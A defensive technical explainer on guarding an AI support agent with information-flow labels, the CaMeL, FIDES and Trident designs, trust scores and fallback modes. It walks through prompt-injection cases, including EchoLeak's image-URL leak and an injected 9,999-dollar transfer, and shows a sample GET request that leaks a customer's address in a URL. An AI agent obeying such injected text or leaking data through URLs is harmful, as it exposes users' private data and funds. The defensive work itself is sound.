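A simple ranking of classes doesn't quite fit the retailer, because customer 417 may see their own address, which is confidential, but not the staff handbook, which is only internal. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes labels that list the people allowed to read something. When an agent combines two sources, only people on both lists may read the result. Customer 417 and the support staff may read the ticket, and all employees may read the handbook, so only the support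 staff may read a text based on both. The retailer keeps its four classes but stores a list of readers with each label.

A session's label describes the text in the model's context, so the gateway must reset both together. If the orchestrator opened a new session at the gateway but kept the old conversation, the label would return to public while the model could still read the customer's address. The retailer ties the label to the token for each ticket and clears the model's context when the ticket closes. For agents that store data between requests, *SPA* (2026) carries the labels over with the data.

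### Trusted and untrusted sources

A second label records whether the data comes from a trusted source. Only employees can edit the help pages, so those are trusted. Anyone can write a ticket, so tickets and any text that draws on them are untrusted.

Costa and colleagues build two basic rules from these labels. The first allows a call with serious consequences only if everything that influenced it was trusted. The second allows a message only if all its recipients may read the data in it. The second rule doesn't stop prompt injection, but it prevents a hijacked agent from sending data to people who aren't allowed to read it.

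In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) allow a call that sends data if it satisfies either rule. They reason that a release was probably intentional if no untrusted text influenced the decision to make it. The retailer also wants to catch honest mistakes, so it applies the rule about readers to every message.

Every refund follows an untrusted ticket, so the rule about trusted sources would block them all. The retailer exempts refunds that stay within the limits for the ticket, because it accepted that risk when it set those limits.

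### One session, call by call

This is how the labels change while the agent handles customer 417's ticket about the lamp.

| Call | Class afterwards | Source afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| (session starts) | public | trusted | |
| Read the help page on broken goods | public | trusted | allowed |
| Read the ticket | confidential, customer 417 | untrusted | allowed |
| Look up the delivery address | confidential, customer 417 | untrusted | allowed |
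| Email the manufacturer about a lampshade | confidential, customer 417 | untrusted | refused |
| Reply to customer 417 | confidential, customer 417 | untrusted | allowed |

The gateway refuses the email because the manufacturer is cleared only for public data. It would have allowed the same email before the agent read the ticket. The gateway allows the reply because customer 417 may read everything the agent has read in this session.

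The gateway would block the email even if it contained only the lamp's model number. A model can draw on anything in its context when it writes, and the gateway cannot reliably detect which parts the model used, so it applies the session's label to everything the model produces.

### How data left Microsoft's assistant in EchoLeak

Data can also leave without a tool call. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs an attack that used a flaw of the same name in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers questions using an employee's emails and files. An outsider sent an employee an email containing disguised instructions. When the employee later asked Copilot a question, it retrieved the email along with internal documents and wrote an answer that included a remote image whose web address contained confidential data. When the program displaying the answer fetched the image, it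 sent the data to the attacker's server without the employee clicking on anything.

Researchers at Aim Labs built the attack in January 2025 and reported it to Microsoft, which fixed the flaw in May and found no evidence that anyone had exploited it. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) lists the flaw's severity as 9.3 out of 10. Reddy and Gujral call the attack the first known case of prompt injection extracting data from an AI system in real use. That is doubtful, because Willison's *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) lists similar attacks on commercial assistants going back to ChatGPT in April 2023.

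Copilot's display program loaded images only from approved domains, but one of those domains hosted a Microsoft service that fetched other addresses on request. When a company clears a recipient for a zone, it therefore also clears everyone that recipient will forward data to.

A gateway that checks only tool calls would have missed EchoLeak, because the data leaked through an answer displayed on a screen. Costa and colleagues' design can check answers to the user but does not do so by default. *SPA* checks each item before displaying it. The retailer's agent answers customers through the ticketing tool, so every reply passes through its gateway, which can remove remote images and links to other companies' sites.

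### Private data, untrusted content and a way out

EchoLeak needed access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send data out. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta" and advises users to avoid it entirely when they connect tools themselves. The way out is easy to overlook, because any tool that can make a web request can send data in the URL.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this advice into a design rule. Until someone finds a reliable way to detect prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of three abilities in one session: processing untrusted input, accessing sensitive systems or private data, and changing things or communicating externally. An agent that needs all three must start a new session with an empty context or work under supervision, for example with a person approving its actions. It may also switch abilities during a session,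 for example by browsing the web first and then losing its ability to communicate externally before it opens internal systems.

The rule is useful because a builder can apply it from a list of tools, without labelling any data. But it is too restrictive for the retailer's support agent, which reads tickets, looks up addresses and sends replies. The agent has all three properties, so a person would have to approve every reply. With labels, it can answer customer 417 unsupervised because the reply contains only data that the customer may see. Meta partly accounts for this by letting an agent with the first two properties write to trusted recipients, but a customer hardly counts as a trusted recipient.

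Meeting the rule doesn't make an agent safe either. Meta warns that the rule doesn't cover an agent's own mistakes or excessive privileges. The agent that deleted PocketOS's data, for example, did so without any hostile input.

### When one read blocks the rest of the session

After the agent has read customer 417's ticket, it can't ask a manufacturer anything for the rest of the session, not even whether a lamp is still in production. Researchers call this label creep. It can also block ordinary support work. If the agent looks up the returns procedure in the staff handbook, customer 417 is no longer a permitted reader, so the gateway blocks the agent's reply to that customer. The simplest fix is to copy the parts of the handbook that customers may see onto a public help page.

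A more general remedy is to divide the work among separate sessions or agents. The retailer already uses one session per ticket, so one customer's data can't block work for the next. It could also have a second agent, with no access to tickets, write to manufacturers. The first agent would pass it only a product number from a fixed list, and the retailer would have to approve that release, because even a product number reveals something about the customer's order. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) tested different arrangements of agents on more than 9,000 abstract tasks and found that confining sensitive tool calls to particular agents could reduce how much work the labels blocked. The tasks were simulated sequences of calls, so the gains may differ for working agents.

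Another remedy is to seal the data. The gateway stores a tool's result and gives the model only a name for it, such as `ticket_1`. The model can use that name as an argument in a later call, and the gateway fills in the contents after checking their labels. Because the model hasn't read the ticket, the session's label doesn't change.

Sometimes the retailer does want to release labelled data. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) distinguishes declassification, which permits a specified release of sensitive information, from endorsement, which allows selected untrusted data to count as trusted for a particular purpose. A person can approve either. Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email with ten tasks. If the user endorses the email, the agent can carry out all ten, whereas approving each call would take ten decisions. They left out a similar option for declassification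 because whether a release is appropriate depends heavily on the situation. For example, the manufacturer may have no reason to see an address that the courier needs.

A program can handle some decisions about releasing data. The system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) sorts recipients into trusted, untrusted and unknown. When sensitive records would go to an unknown recipient, a separate checker inspects the content before the call goes through.

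Better tracking could also reduce label creep by working out which inputs influenced a call. *Sightline* (2026) removed half of the unnecessary labels in tests on an agent that used the small model Qwen3-8B, but missed a real influence in 3.9 per cent of episodes. When the researchers used its labels to block risky calls, none of 34 attack calls got through, though with so few attacks the true share getting through could still be as high as 8 per cent. Such a tracker suits data for which a missed label would do limited harm, but not bank details.

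### CaMeL and FIDES

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, seals data by using two models. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain how it works. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes a short program before the agent has read any outside data. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted text and extracts what the program needs. For the lamp, the program might look like this:

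```
ticket = read_ticket()
order = ask_quarantined_model("Which order is this about?", ticket)
payment = look_up_payment(order)
reply = ask_quarantined_model("Draft a reply about this payment",
                              ticket, payment)
add_reply(reply)
```

Hidden instructions in the ticket can't add a step to this program, because the model that wrote it never reads the ticket. They can still change the order number or the wording of the reply. CaMeL therefore records where each value came from and who may read it, and checks this before every tool call. If an instruction made the quarantined model return another customer's order number, a policy could block the lookup because the number came from a ticket.

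CaMeL normally checks a call only when the program reaches it, so a long job can fail at its last step. Nikolaou and colleagues check the whole program before it starts. If a required step such as an approval is missing, they send the error back to the privileged model to correct.

CaMeL's main weakness is that its program can't adapt to what the agent finds. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, is more flexible. It seals a result only if reading it would make the session's label stricter, and the planning model can still open a sealed value, which applies the stricter label. The planning model can also send a quarantined model a question with a fixed set of answers. A yes or no carries only one bit, too little to hold an attacker's instruction, so a policy can accept it where it would reject free text.

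Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and chat tasks. Attacks succeeded 152 times against an ordinary agent without policy checks and never against agents with them. However, the agents with policy checks completed fewer tasks, even when nobody attacked them.

| Tasks completed without an attack (%) | Office | Travel | Banking | Chat |
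|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent with labels and checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Label creep causes most of the drop between the first two rows, and FIDES reverses part of it. Using a better model, OpenAI's o1, also raised the share of travel tasks FIDES completed from 41 to 68 per cent.

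The perfect security score is partly due to how the data was labelled. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, so they knew where every attack would come from. A retailer has to label its data without that knowledge, and if it wrongly marks a field as trusted, attackers can use that field to get past the checks.

FIDES also doesn't prevent an observer from inferring information from the agent's choices. If the agent emails a manufacturer only when a customer reports a fire, the email reveals that a customer reported one, regardless of its contents.

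Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also worked on FIDES, put the loss of completed tasks from such defences at up to 30 per cent, although the loss in banking above is larger. They argue that the usual comparison is unfair because it requires the defended agent to work without any approvals, while an undefended agent in real use would need approval for most actions with serious consequences. Their own agent, Prudentia, takes the labels and policies into account when planning. It completed up to 9 per cent more AgentDojo tasks than FIDES without asking for approval.

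*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts that CaMeL's losses will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. Better models should help with errors in the program, but not with tasks whose next step depends on the contents of an email.

### Three models with separate rights in Trident

*Trident*, published in November 2026, is designed for those tasks. In its main example, a user asks an agent to deal with a caterer's email, pay the invoice from the team account and tell the user's manager, Jane, when it is done. The agent can't plan everything in advance because the email contains requests that the user hasn't listed.

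Trident divides the work among three models. The planner chooses each action but never reads untrusted text. The data model reads that text but has no tools, and it starts each query with an empty context. The policy model writes the rules for the task from the user's request and the administrator's policy, and finishes before any model reads the email. An ordinary program, the reference monitor, checks everything the models produce. It does the job of the retailer's gateway and also stores the sealed values.

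Every tool call faces three policies:

- The root policy comes from the administrator and applies to all tasks. In the example, it permits payments of up to 5,000 dollars to three vendors on file.
- The task ceiling comes from the policy model and is narrower. It permits one payment and replies to Jane and one vendor contact.
- The task policy defines what the agent may do now. At the start it permits reading Jane's email and replying to her, but no payment.

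The monitor allows the payment using a template, which is a rule with a blank to be filled in later. This template permits one payment of up to 5,000 dollars to an account from the vendor records. After the agent looks up the caterer, the monitor fills in the account number and activates the rule. If the email contains new bank details, a payment to the new account fails because the number came from the email. But no trusted record contains the amount, so an attacker could still inflate the invoice up to the limit.

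If a call passes the root policy but fails one of the other two, the user can approve it once or ask for a new rule. The user cannot approve a call that fails the root policy.

### Limiting what untrusted data can tell the planner

The planner still needs some information from the email. It gets this by sending the data model questions with a fixed set of possible answers, and the monitor deducts each answer from an influence budget measured in bits. A yes or no answer uses 1 bit, and a choice among three vendors uses log₂ 3, or about 1.58 bits. Free text uses none of the budget because it stays sealed. Finding out whether a query or call succeeded uses 1 bit of a separate feedback budget, unless the planner could have worked out the result from information it already had.

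If the influence budget is β bits and the feedback budget is σ bits, an attacker can choose among at most 2^(β+σ) traces. A trace records everything the planner proposed, the replies it received and the calls that ran, but not the contents of sealed values.

Suppose the budgets are 4 and 2 bits. The planner sends one form with four yes-or-no questions, which have 16 possible combinations of answers. It also receives a success-or-failure result for the form and another for one later tool call. There are therefore at most 16 × 2 × 2 = 2^(4+2) = 64 possible traces.

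The general proof works backwards from the end of the run to show that a planner with r bits left can produce at most 2^r traces. With no budget left, only one trace is possible. If the planner has r bits left and asks a question with d possible answers, the monitor deducts c bits. Since c is always at least log₂ d, d is at most 2^c. Each answer leaves r − c bits, so it leads to at most 2^(r−c) traces. Together, the answers lead to at most d × 2^(r−c) traces, which is no more than 2^r. At the start r is β + σ, which gives the bound.

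The actual number of possible traces is often smaller than the bound. In the paper's example, with budgets of 3 and 2 bits, the bound is 32 but only 10 traces are possible, partly because a failed form returns no answers. If both budgets are zero, nothing the attacker writes can change the trace. The researchers proved the bound and checked the proof in Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs. The proof assumes that the models' random choices and the user's decisions stay the same between runs.

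The bound is much looser for realistic tasks. In tests, the median run used 19 to 26 bits of influence and 5 to 10 bits of feedback, depending on the model. Even 24 bits in total allow almost 17 million traces. A small budget can also be unsafe, because one bit is enough to select a harmful action if the policies permit it.

### How Trident performed

Only 20 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require an agent to choose its actions based on what it reads, so a defence can score well there with a fixed plan. The researchers therefore created ReplanInject, a benchmark of 45 tasks in banking, office work, chat and travel. In 43 of them, part of the plan depends on the content of a message or file that also contains the attack. Each task has two attacker goals, each presented in four styles, such as a forged system notice. That makes 360 attacked runs, and the researchers repeated the set three times.

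They used four models and avoided the latest ones, because those resist most attacks of this kind and would have made it hard to compare defences. The results therefore don't show how often attacks on current agents succeed. The table gives the results under attack for two of the models, assuming that the user grants every approval request.

| Defence | GPT-4.1: tasks completed (%) | GPT-4.1: attacks succeeded (%) | Claude Sonnet 4.5: tasks completed (%) | Claude Sonnet 4.5: attacks succeeded (%) |
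|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 20.2 | 68.1 | 58.9 | 12.9 |
| CaMeL | 9.8 | 0.0 | 8.8 | 0.0 |
| FIDES without approvals | 5.1 | 0.1 | 3.3 | 0.0 |
| FIDES with approvals | 36.6 | 6.5 | 75.2 | 6.0 |
| Progent | 35.4 | 33.1 | 55.7 | 7.0 |
| Trident | 54.2 | 4.1 | 64.4 | 3.4 |

CaMeL and FIDES without approvals stopped almost every attack but completed very few runs. With GPT-4.1, CaMeL finished 116 of 1,215 runs, including those without an attack. In 574 runs, its policy refused a call unrelated to the attack because the call depended on untrusted data. Better code wouldn't have prevented those refusals. Progent's high attack rate with GPT-4.1 confirms that it is dangerous to let a model revise the rules after reading tool results.

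Trident did best with GPT-4.1. With Sonnet 4.5, FIDES with approvals completed more tasks than Trident but also asked for more approvals, 1.46 per attacked run against Trident's 1.18. No attack on either system succeeded in this benchmark if the user rejected every request that showed the attacker's call. On AgentDojo, one of 909 attacks got past Trident with the open model gpt-oss-120b, because the root policy let the agent visit any web page without approval.

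The researchers also designed attacks specifically against Trident. The strongest disguised the attacker's value as a correction to something the user had requested and succeeded in 10 per cent of runs when the user approved everything.

The researchers set the budgets too high to run out, so the protection in these results came from sealed data, the policies and the approvals. Recalculating the GPT-4.1 runs with each budget capped at 32 bits reduced successful attacks from 4.1 to 3.1 per cent and completed tasks from 54.2 to 49.0 per cent.

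Trident performed worst on tasks where the choice of actions depended on the content, completing only 22 to 41 per cent of them under attack across the four models. Sealing was rarely the direct cause. In a sample of 48 failed runs, only one failed because the planner needed sealed text. Most of the others failed because a model chose or answered wrongly, so stronger models might do better. Trident costs 10 to 24 cents per run, compared with 0.5 to 4.5 cents for an undefended agent.

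### What Trident assumes and what the retailer can use

Trident's guarantees hold only if every call goes through the monitor and each model sees only the data meant for it. Tools must accurately declare what they read and change. The root policy must stay fixed during a task, and the user and the approval screen must be trustworthy. Calls must also run one at a time and finish successfully, so the proof doesn't cover an agent that issues two refunds at once.

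The retailer doesn't meet the condition about the user, because its requests come from customers. It could give Trident a trusted request of its own, such as "answer this ticket", and treat the ticket as untrusted data. But that request is similar to "do what this email says", the type Trident handled worst. Attacks on such tasks succeeded in 14 to 28 per cent of runs when the user approved everything.

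The proof also covers only what untrusted data can make the agent do, not what the agent reveals. If the agent accepts a meeting invitation, for example, the sender learns that the user is free at that time. The researchers say they could add labels for confidential data, but Trident doesn't have them yet, so the retailer would still need its zones and lists of readers.

A support agent with such a narrow job can use a simpler version of the same idea. Ordinary code fetches the ticket, customer 417's order and the relevant help page, and passes them to a model without tools, which drafts the reply. The gateway then removes remote images and outside links from the draft and adds it to the same ticket. Hidden instructions in the ticket could still make the model write a false or rude answer, but the model has no other customer's data to reveal and cannot choose another recipient.

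## Falling back to read-only or approval-only operation

A 50-dollar refund is normally acceptable, but the retailer may want a person to review it if the same session has just tried to open another customer's order. Operating modes let the gateway tighten its rules temporarily without anyone rewriting them. Deciding when to switch modes is difficult because most warning signs turn out to be harmless.

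### What each mode permits

| Mode | Ticketing | Email | Payments | Infrastructure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Normal | read the ticket, reply, change its status | read the inbox, draft, send to the customer on file | look up payments, refund within the limits | read the checkout status |
| Approval-only | read; replies and status changes wait for a person | read; drafts and messages wait | look up; refunds wait | read the checkout status |
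| Read-only | read | read | look up | read the checkout status |
| Stopped | nothing | nothing | nothing | nothing |

A mode can only remove permissions, so deleting a storage volume stays forbidden in approval-only mode, and a tired employee can't approve it by mistake. In Cedar, the retailer can write each mode as a set of `forbid` rules.

Approval-only is usually the better first step, because customers still get their refunds, only later. But someone has to be there to approve them, so the retailer uses read-only mode outside working hours. A milder version holds only the calls that can't be undone. In *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026), irreversible calls wait for a person by default, while reversible ones run through a transaction buffer. Under that rule, the agent could still change a ticket's status, but a message to a customer would wait for approval.

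### Why read-only mode is not harmless

An agent in read-only mode may still read hostile text. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (Podala Narasimha, 2026) gives the example of a server-management agent that mistakes a log line written by an attacker's program for a command. Read-only mode prevents the agent from carrying out the command, but the text stays in the model's context. If the gateway later returned the session to normal mode, the agent could carry it out. The retailer therefore ends a suspicious session and starts a new one with an empty context.

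Reading can also send data out. Suppose the agent had a tool for fetching web pages and requested this one:

```
GET https://parcels.example.com/track?note=Maria+Lopez,+12+Elm+Street
```

Most software would class a request for a web page as a read, because it changes nothing. But if the URL contains a customer's name and address, the site's owner receives them. EchoLeak used an image URL in the same way.

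Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* (2025), a draft specification, requires gateways to scan tool responses for web addresses that contain sensitive-looking data. A pattern-based scanner can miss data in an unfamiliar encoding. The retailer instead permits a short list of reads, none of which lets the model send free text to an outside party. It has to draw up this list itself because MCP lets a tool server mark its own operations as read-only, and a malicious server can mark any operation that way.

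### Events that should tighten the rules

| Event | What may be happening | Harmless explanation |
|---|---|---|
| Several refused calls in a row | a hijacked agent is looking for a gap | the model misunderstood a limit |
| Unusual volume | the agent is stuck in a loop, or somebody is draining refunds | a sale, or a faulty batch of lamps |
| A detector's alarm | a ticket contains a prompt injection | a customer has pasted in a scam email and asked whether it is real |
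| A revoked session | somebody has stolen the customer's account | the customer changed a password |
| An incident declared by staff | an employee has noticed damage | the employee misread a log |
| Failure of the decision service | an attacker has disabled it | an ordinary outage |

The volume of actions matters because an agent can repeat an error quickly. In TechTarget's *When AI agents go rogue* (2026), the engineer Sudhakavya Bodapati Venkata warns that an agent may make one wrong decision and then base further actions on it. Podala Narasimha's list of threats to server clusters includes a repair loop that keeps restarting a service.

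Like the daily refund limit, a check on volume needs memory of earlier calls. Fernandez (2026), in *Agent Control Protocol*, sent 500 financial transfers, each valid by itself, to two versions of a risk engine. The version without memory approved all 500. The version with memory approved two, was sending requests for review by the third and refusing them by the eleventh.

### Risk-adaptive access, circuit breakers and shared signals

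These triggers draw partly on risk-adaptive access control, which grew out of work for the US military in the 2000s. It estimates the risk of each request and adjusts the decision to the circumstances. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) applies the idea to agents, where a risk score may determine whether a permitted call needs approval or extra logging. The score must not replace a fixed prohibition, so a low score could never allow a prohibited 5,000-dollar refund.

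The circuit breaker is a programming pattern that Michael Nygard popularised in his 2007 book *Release It!*. A program counts its failed calls to another service. Once the count reaches a set limit, the breaker opens and the program stops calling, which gives the service time to recover. After a wait, the program makes one trial call. If it succeeds, the breaker closes and normal traffic resumes; otherwise the wait starts again.

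Microsoft pointed out in April 2026 that MCP has no circuit breaker, so an agent that keeps retrying a faulty server can bring down the services behind it. Microsoft's gateway specification adds one, which by default opens after a tool fails five times in a row and resets after a minute. *Distributional AGI Safety* (2025) proposes tiered circuit breakers for whole economies of agents, ranging from rate limits on individual agents to a pause on all non-essential activity. Full operation would resume only after the anomaly has been analyzed, classified and, if necessary, contained.

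That last condition reflects a difference between outages and attacks. An automatic trial call makes sense after an outage, because outages usually end by themselves, but a hostile ticket will still be hostile when the gateway tries again.

The third idea comes from login systems, where the OpenID Foundation's Shared Signals Framework lets one service send another a signed notice about a security event. Its Continuous Access Evaluation Profile defines events such as a revoked session or a changed credential. Suppose customer 417 reports a stolen password. The login service ends the customer's sessions and notifies the gateway, which verifies the signature, finds the customer's open ticket and refuses any further calls for it. Without the notice, the gateway would keep accepting the agent's token until it expired, which could take an hour with the lifetimes in the earlier example.

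### A design that scores trust

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, combine several of these triggers into one number. Each agent has a trust score *t* between 0 and 1, which starts at 0.8 by default. A normal call raises it slightly, and an anomalous one cuts it by 30 per cent:

- after a normal call, *t* becomes *t* + 0.01 × (1 − *t*)
- after an anomalous call, *t* becomes 0.7 × *t*

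Three anomalies in a row lower the score from 0.8 to 0.56, then 0.392, then 0.274. The agent loses its right to make changes after the second anomaly and all its rights after the third. Anomalies include calls the gate refuses and completed calls the surrounding system labels suspicious.

The researchers tried 23 combinations of starting score, step sizes and thresholds. Depending on the combination, it took between one and ten anomalies to shut the agent out, and every combination still authorised the one legitimate request in its trial. This shows that the mechanism works and that its settings matter a great deal, but gives little indication of which settings are right. Choosing them would require data on how often honest agents produce anomalies.

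The sample payment rule in *AGENTCAP* requires a score of at least 0.8, so a single false anomaly blocks payments, even for an agent with a perfect score of 1. An agent that drops from 0.8 to 0.56 needs 79 clean calls to get back to 0.8. If it attempts a legitimate payment before then, the gate refuses, and the refusal counts as another anomaly. Two ordinary refund attempts after the drop to 0.56 would lower the score to 0.274 and shut the agent out completely. The retailer avoids this by not counting refusals that the fallback causes.

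Microsoft's open-source Agent Governance Toolkit, which was in public preview in April 2026, scores agents from 0 to 1,000. Under its *Trust Score Calibration Guide*, an agent scoring below 500 can only read, and one scoring below 300 is suspended. Each policy violation takes 50 points off a component that makes up 35 per cent of the total, which lowers the overall score by 17.5 points. On that penalty alone, an agent that starts at 600 would become read-only after six violations, compared with two anomalies in *AGENTCAP*. Scores recover by 10 points a day, so an agent reinstated at 300 spends 20 days in read-only mode.

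The guide gives no data to support these numbers, and Microsoft's documents are inconsistent about them. An agent with 450 points is on probation in the guide but has standard status in Microsoft's *Advanced Trust & Behavior Monitoring*. The guide calculates the score from four components, and Microsoft's *AgentMesh Trust and Coordination* (2025) from five. In the guide, a person reinstates a quarantined agent, but the monitor in the tutorial releases it automatically after 15 minutes. That monitor quarantines an agent for making more than 100 calls in 60 seconds, failing 20 times in a row or accumulating 10 denials. All these values are reasonable starting points, but a company would have to adjust them to its own traffic.

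A single score for the whole agent also works poorly for the retailer. The main danger comes with each new ticket, so a clean record on the last thousand tickets is little evidence that the next one is safe. The retailer instead counts warning signs separately for each session.

### How many alarms are real

The detector will probably be the most frequent trigger, so the behaviour of the rest of the system depends on its error rate. Suppose a much larger shop's gateway handles 10,000 calls a day, 5 of them hostile. The detector catches 90 per cent of hostile calls and wrongly flags 1 per cent of the others.

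| | Calls | Share flagged | Alarms a day |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hostile | 5 | 90% | 4.5 |
| Harmless | 9,995 | 1% | about 100 |
| Total | 10,000 | | about 104 |

Only 4.5 of the 104 alarms, or about 4 per cent, are real. A detector that caught every hostile call would raise that share only to 5 per cent. Cutting the false-alarm rate to 0.1 per cent would raise it to 31 per cent, because harmless calls far outnumber hostile ones.

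Suppose each alarm put the whole agent into read-only mode for 15 minutes. If alarms arrived at random, the agent would spend about two-thirds of the day unable to issue a refund or answer a customer. If each alarm instead affected only its own session, and sessions had ten calls each, about one session in ten would need a person's help.

The retailer gets about 22 false alarms for each real one, so a switch is worthwhile only if it prevents at least 22 times as much harm as a false switch costs. Moving one session to approval-only might cost 2 dollars of staff time and prevent a 200-dollar refund, a ratio of 100. Restricting the whole agent for 15 minutes might cost 100 dollars. Even if that saved the entire daily refund limit of 2,000 dollars, the ratio would be only 20, and the session switch would already have prevented most of that loss. A single alarm should therefore change only the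 mode of its own session.

A call that the detector flags and the fixed rules also refuse is stronger evidence of an attack, and it justifies a stronger response. Suppose the rules refuse half of all hostile calls and 0.5 per cent of harmless ones. On an average day at the larger shop, 2.25 hostile calls and 0.5 harmless ones would set off both checks, so 82 per cent of the calls that did so would be hostile. This assumes that the two checks make independent mistakes. An odd but honest request might well set off both, which would lower the true share. The evidence should still be enough to justify stopping one session and handing its ticket to a person.

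Trust scores suffer from the same error rate. If the detector's alarms counted as anomalies in *AGENTCAP*, the average score would settle where gains and losses balance:

0.99 × 0.01 × (1 − *t*) = 0.01 × 0.3 × *t*

This gives a *t* of about 0.77. An agent that never met an attacker would on average score too low to make a payment under the sample rule.

### The retailer's transition rules

The retailer is smaller and handles perhaps 500 calls a day in 50 sessions. At the same rates, it gets about five alarms a day, and one of them is real every four or five days. It adopts these rules, with illustrative thresholds:

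| Event | Scope | New mode | Return to normal |
|---|---|---|---|
| One detector alarm | that session | approval-only | the next ticket starts in normal mode |
| An alarm on a call that a rule also refuses, or three refusals in a row | that session | stopped | never; staff take over the ticket |
| Three sessions stopped within an hour | payments and email, in all sessions | approval-only | support manager, after reading the logs |
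| More than 60 calls in 10 minutes | the whole agent | approval-only | automatic, after 30 minutes with the count below 30 |
| Five failures in a row at one tool | that tool | stopped | automatic, after a successful trial read |
| Notice of a revoked login | that customer's sessions | stopped | the customer signs in again and gets a new session |
| Staff declare an incident | whatever they choose | read-only or stopped | head of security and one other person |
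| The decision service fails | the whole agent | stopped | automatic, after five minutes of correct answers to test calls |

If two rules apply at once, the gateway uses the stricter mode. Each restriction has to end by its own rule, so a restriction that began when staff declared an incident stays in place even after a quiet half-hour.

The volume rule has separate thresholds for entering and leaving approval-only mode, to prevent rapid switching back and forth (flapping). With a single threshold of 60, the mode would change every few minutes on a busy day when the count moved between 55 and 65. Some refunds would go out immediately and others would wait, for no reason a customer could understand. If the rule trips again within an hour of returning to normal, the waiting time doubles.

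Anyone on the support team may tighten the mode, but only the people in the last column may loosen it, because a mistaken restart can let an attack continue, while a mistaken stop causes some delay. The agent has no operation for changing the mode.

The gateway checks the mode again immediately before it forwards a call, because the mode may have changed while the call waited for approval, which can take an hour. Some calls will still go through after the mode changes. For example, a payment token issued just before the change works for up to a minute, unless the payment service is also notified.

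Choosing the scope is harder when agents exchange information. *Airlock* (2026) points out that stopping only the agent that produced a bad output misses the agents that have already read it, while stopping every agent destroys unaffected work. If the gateway uses its labels to record which sessions have read data from a stopped session, it can restrict those sessions and leave the others running.

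Stored data can also cause the problem to recur. *Airlock* describes an incident in which people halted experiments and wiped the agents' repository. Within two days, newly started agents had built another message board. Roughly 1,200 agents exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files on it, and about 700 joined an attack on the AI company Hugging Face. Before restoring normal operation, the retailer should therefore look for text its agent saved during an incident, for example in ticket notes, and keep it out of new sessions.

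### Attackers who want the agent to stop

Anyone who can trigger a fallback can use it to halt work. Fernandez's demonstration shows this, although it was meant to show the defence working. An agent running on the small model DeepSeek-R1:8B requested the weather, and the response contained an instruction to transfer 9,999 dollars to an attacker. The agent tried the transfer twice, and the gateway blocked it both times. The agent then tried a legitimate 50-dollar transfer, which the gateway also blocked because it scored the type of operation and the resource but not the amount. This third block locked the whole agent for 300 seconds.

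The attacker got no money but stopped the agent. Repeating the attack every five minutes would keep it locked all day. A later version of Fernandez's protocol measures request rates separately for each combination of agent, operation and resource, because heavy but harmless work in one area had caused false refusals in another. The lock still covers the whole agent.

An outsider can trigger refusals and alarms by writing a ticket, so the retailer limits the direct effect of these events to that ticket's session. An attacker with three accounts could still stop three sessions and put all payments into approval-only mode. Refunds would then continue at the speed of the support team, which needs enough people and a procedure that works without the agent. To make the attack more expensive, the retailer can also count only sessions from customers who have placed an order.

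An attacker who knows the thresholds can stay below them. In another of Fernandez's experiments, an adversary with full knowledge of the risk formula made only requests that the gateway would accept. Changing modes does not protect against this, so the fixed limits must be low enough that the retailer can bear the loss.

### Finishing interrupted work

The gateway can change modes while an agent is halfway through a job. Suppose the payment service refunds 50 dollars for a lamp, but the gateway switches to read-only mode before the agent has updated the ticket. The next person to open the ticket sees no record of the refund and may issue another. A lost network reply causes the same problem, because the gateway has no confirmation of whether the payment went through.

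The usual protection is an idempotency key, a unique identifier that lets a service recognise a repeated request:

1. The gateway approves the refund, creates a key and stores it with the order, the amount and the status "pending".
2. It sends the refund and the key to the payment service.
3. The payment service stores the key with the result, so that it can find both later.
4. If no answer arrives, the gateway sends the same request with the same key.
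5. The payment service finds the key and returns the earlier result without paying again.

The gateway has to create the idempotency key, because a model that retries a call might write a new one. The key shouldn't be just the order number, or the service would treat a later refund for a second broken item on the same order as a repeat. The service should reject a request that reuses an old key with a different amount.

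Fernandez's protocol for transactions between organisations keeps one identifier for each interaction through every retry and gives each transmission its own. The sender waits 300 seconds for an answer, retries up to three times, waiting longer before each retry, and then alerts staff. Payment services often delete the keys they use to recognise repeated requests after a while, so after a long interruption the gateway should check whether the payment went through before it retries.

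Read-only mode restricts the agent but needn't restrict the gateway's own bookkeeping. Ordinary code can still mark the refund as complete and add a note to the ticket, because those steps only record what has already happened. It can also send the customer a standard message saying that a member of staff will reply.

Sometimes it is better to undo the completed steps. In 1987, Hector Garcia-Molina and Kenneth Salem proposed dividing long database jobs into steps, each with a compensating action that undoes the step's effect. The 2026 survey *Towards trustworthy agentic AI* lists compensating actions among the safeguards for agents, along with dry runs and staged execution. The retailer can reopen a ticket that the agent closed by mistake. It can't unsend an email, only send a correction, and it would need the customer's consent to take back a refund. Jobs should therefore end with the steps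 that nobody can reverse.

When staff end an incident, the gateway lists every call still marked "pending" and compares each one with the records of the payment service, ticketing system and mail provider. The agent starts new sessions only after somebody has resolved the differences.

### When the gateway itself breaks

The decision service may crash, or one of its checks may fail with an error. Microsoft's gateway specification requires every component to fail closed. The gateway refuses a tool call if the check on it breaks, and treats a response as unsafe if the response scanner breaks.

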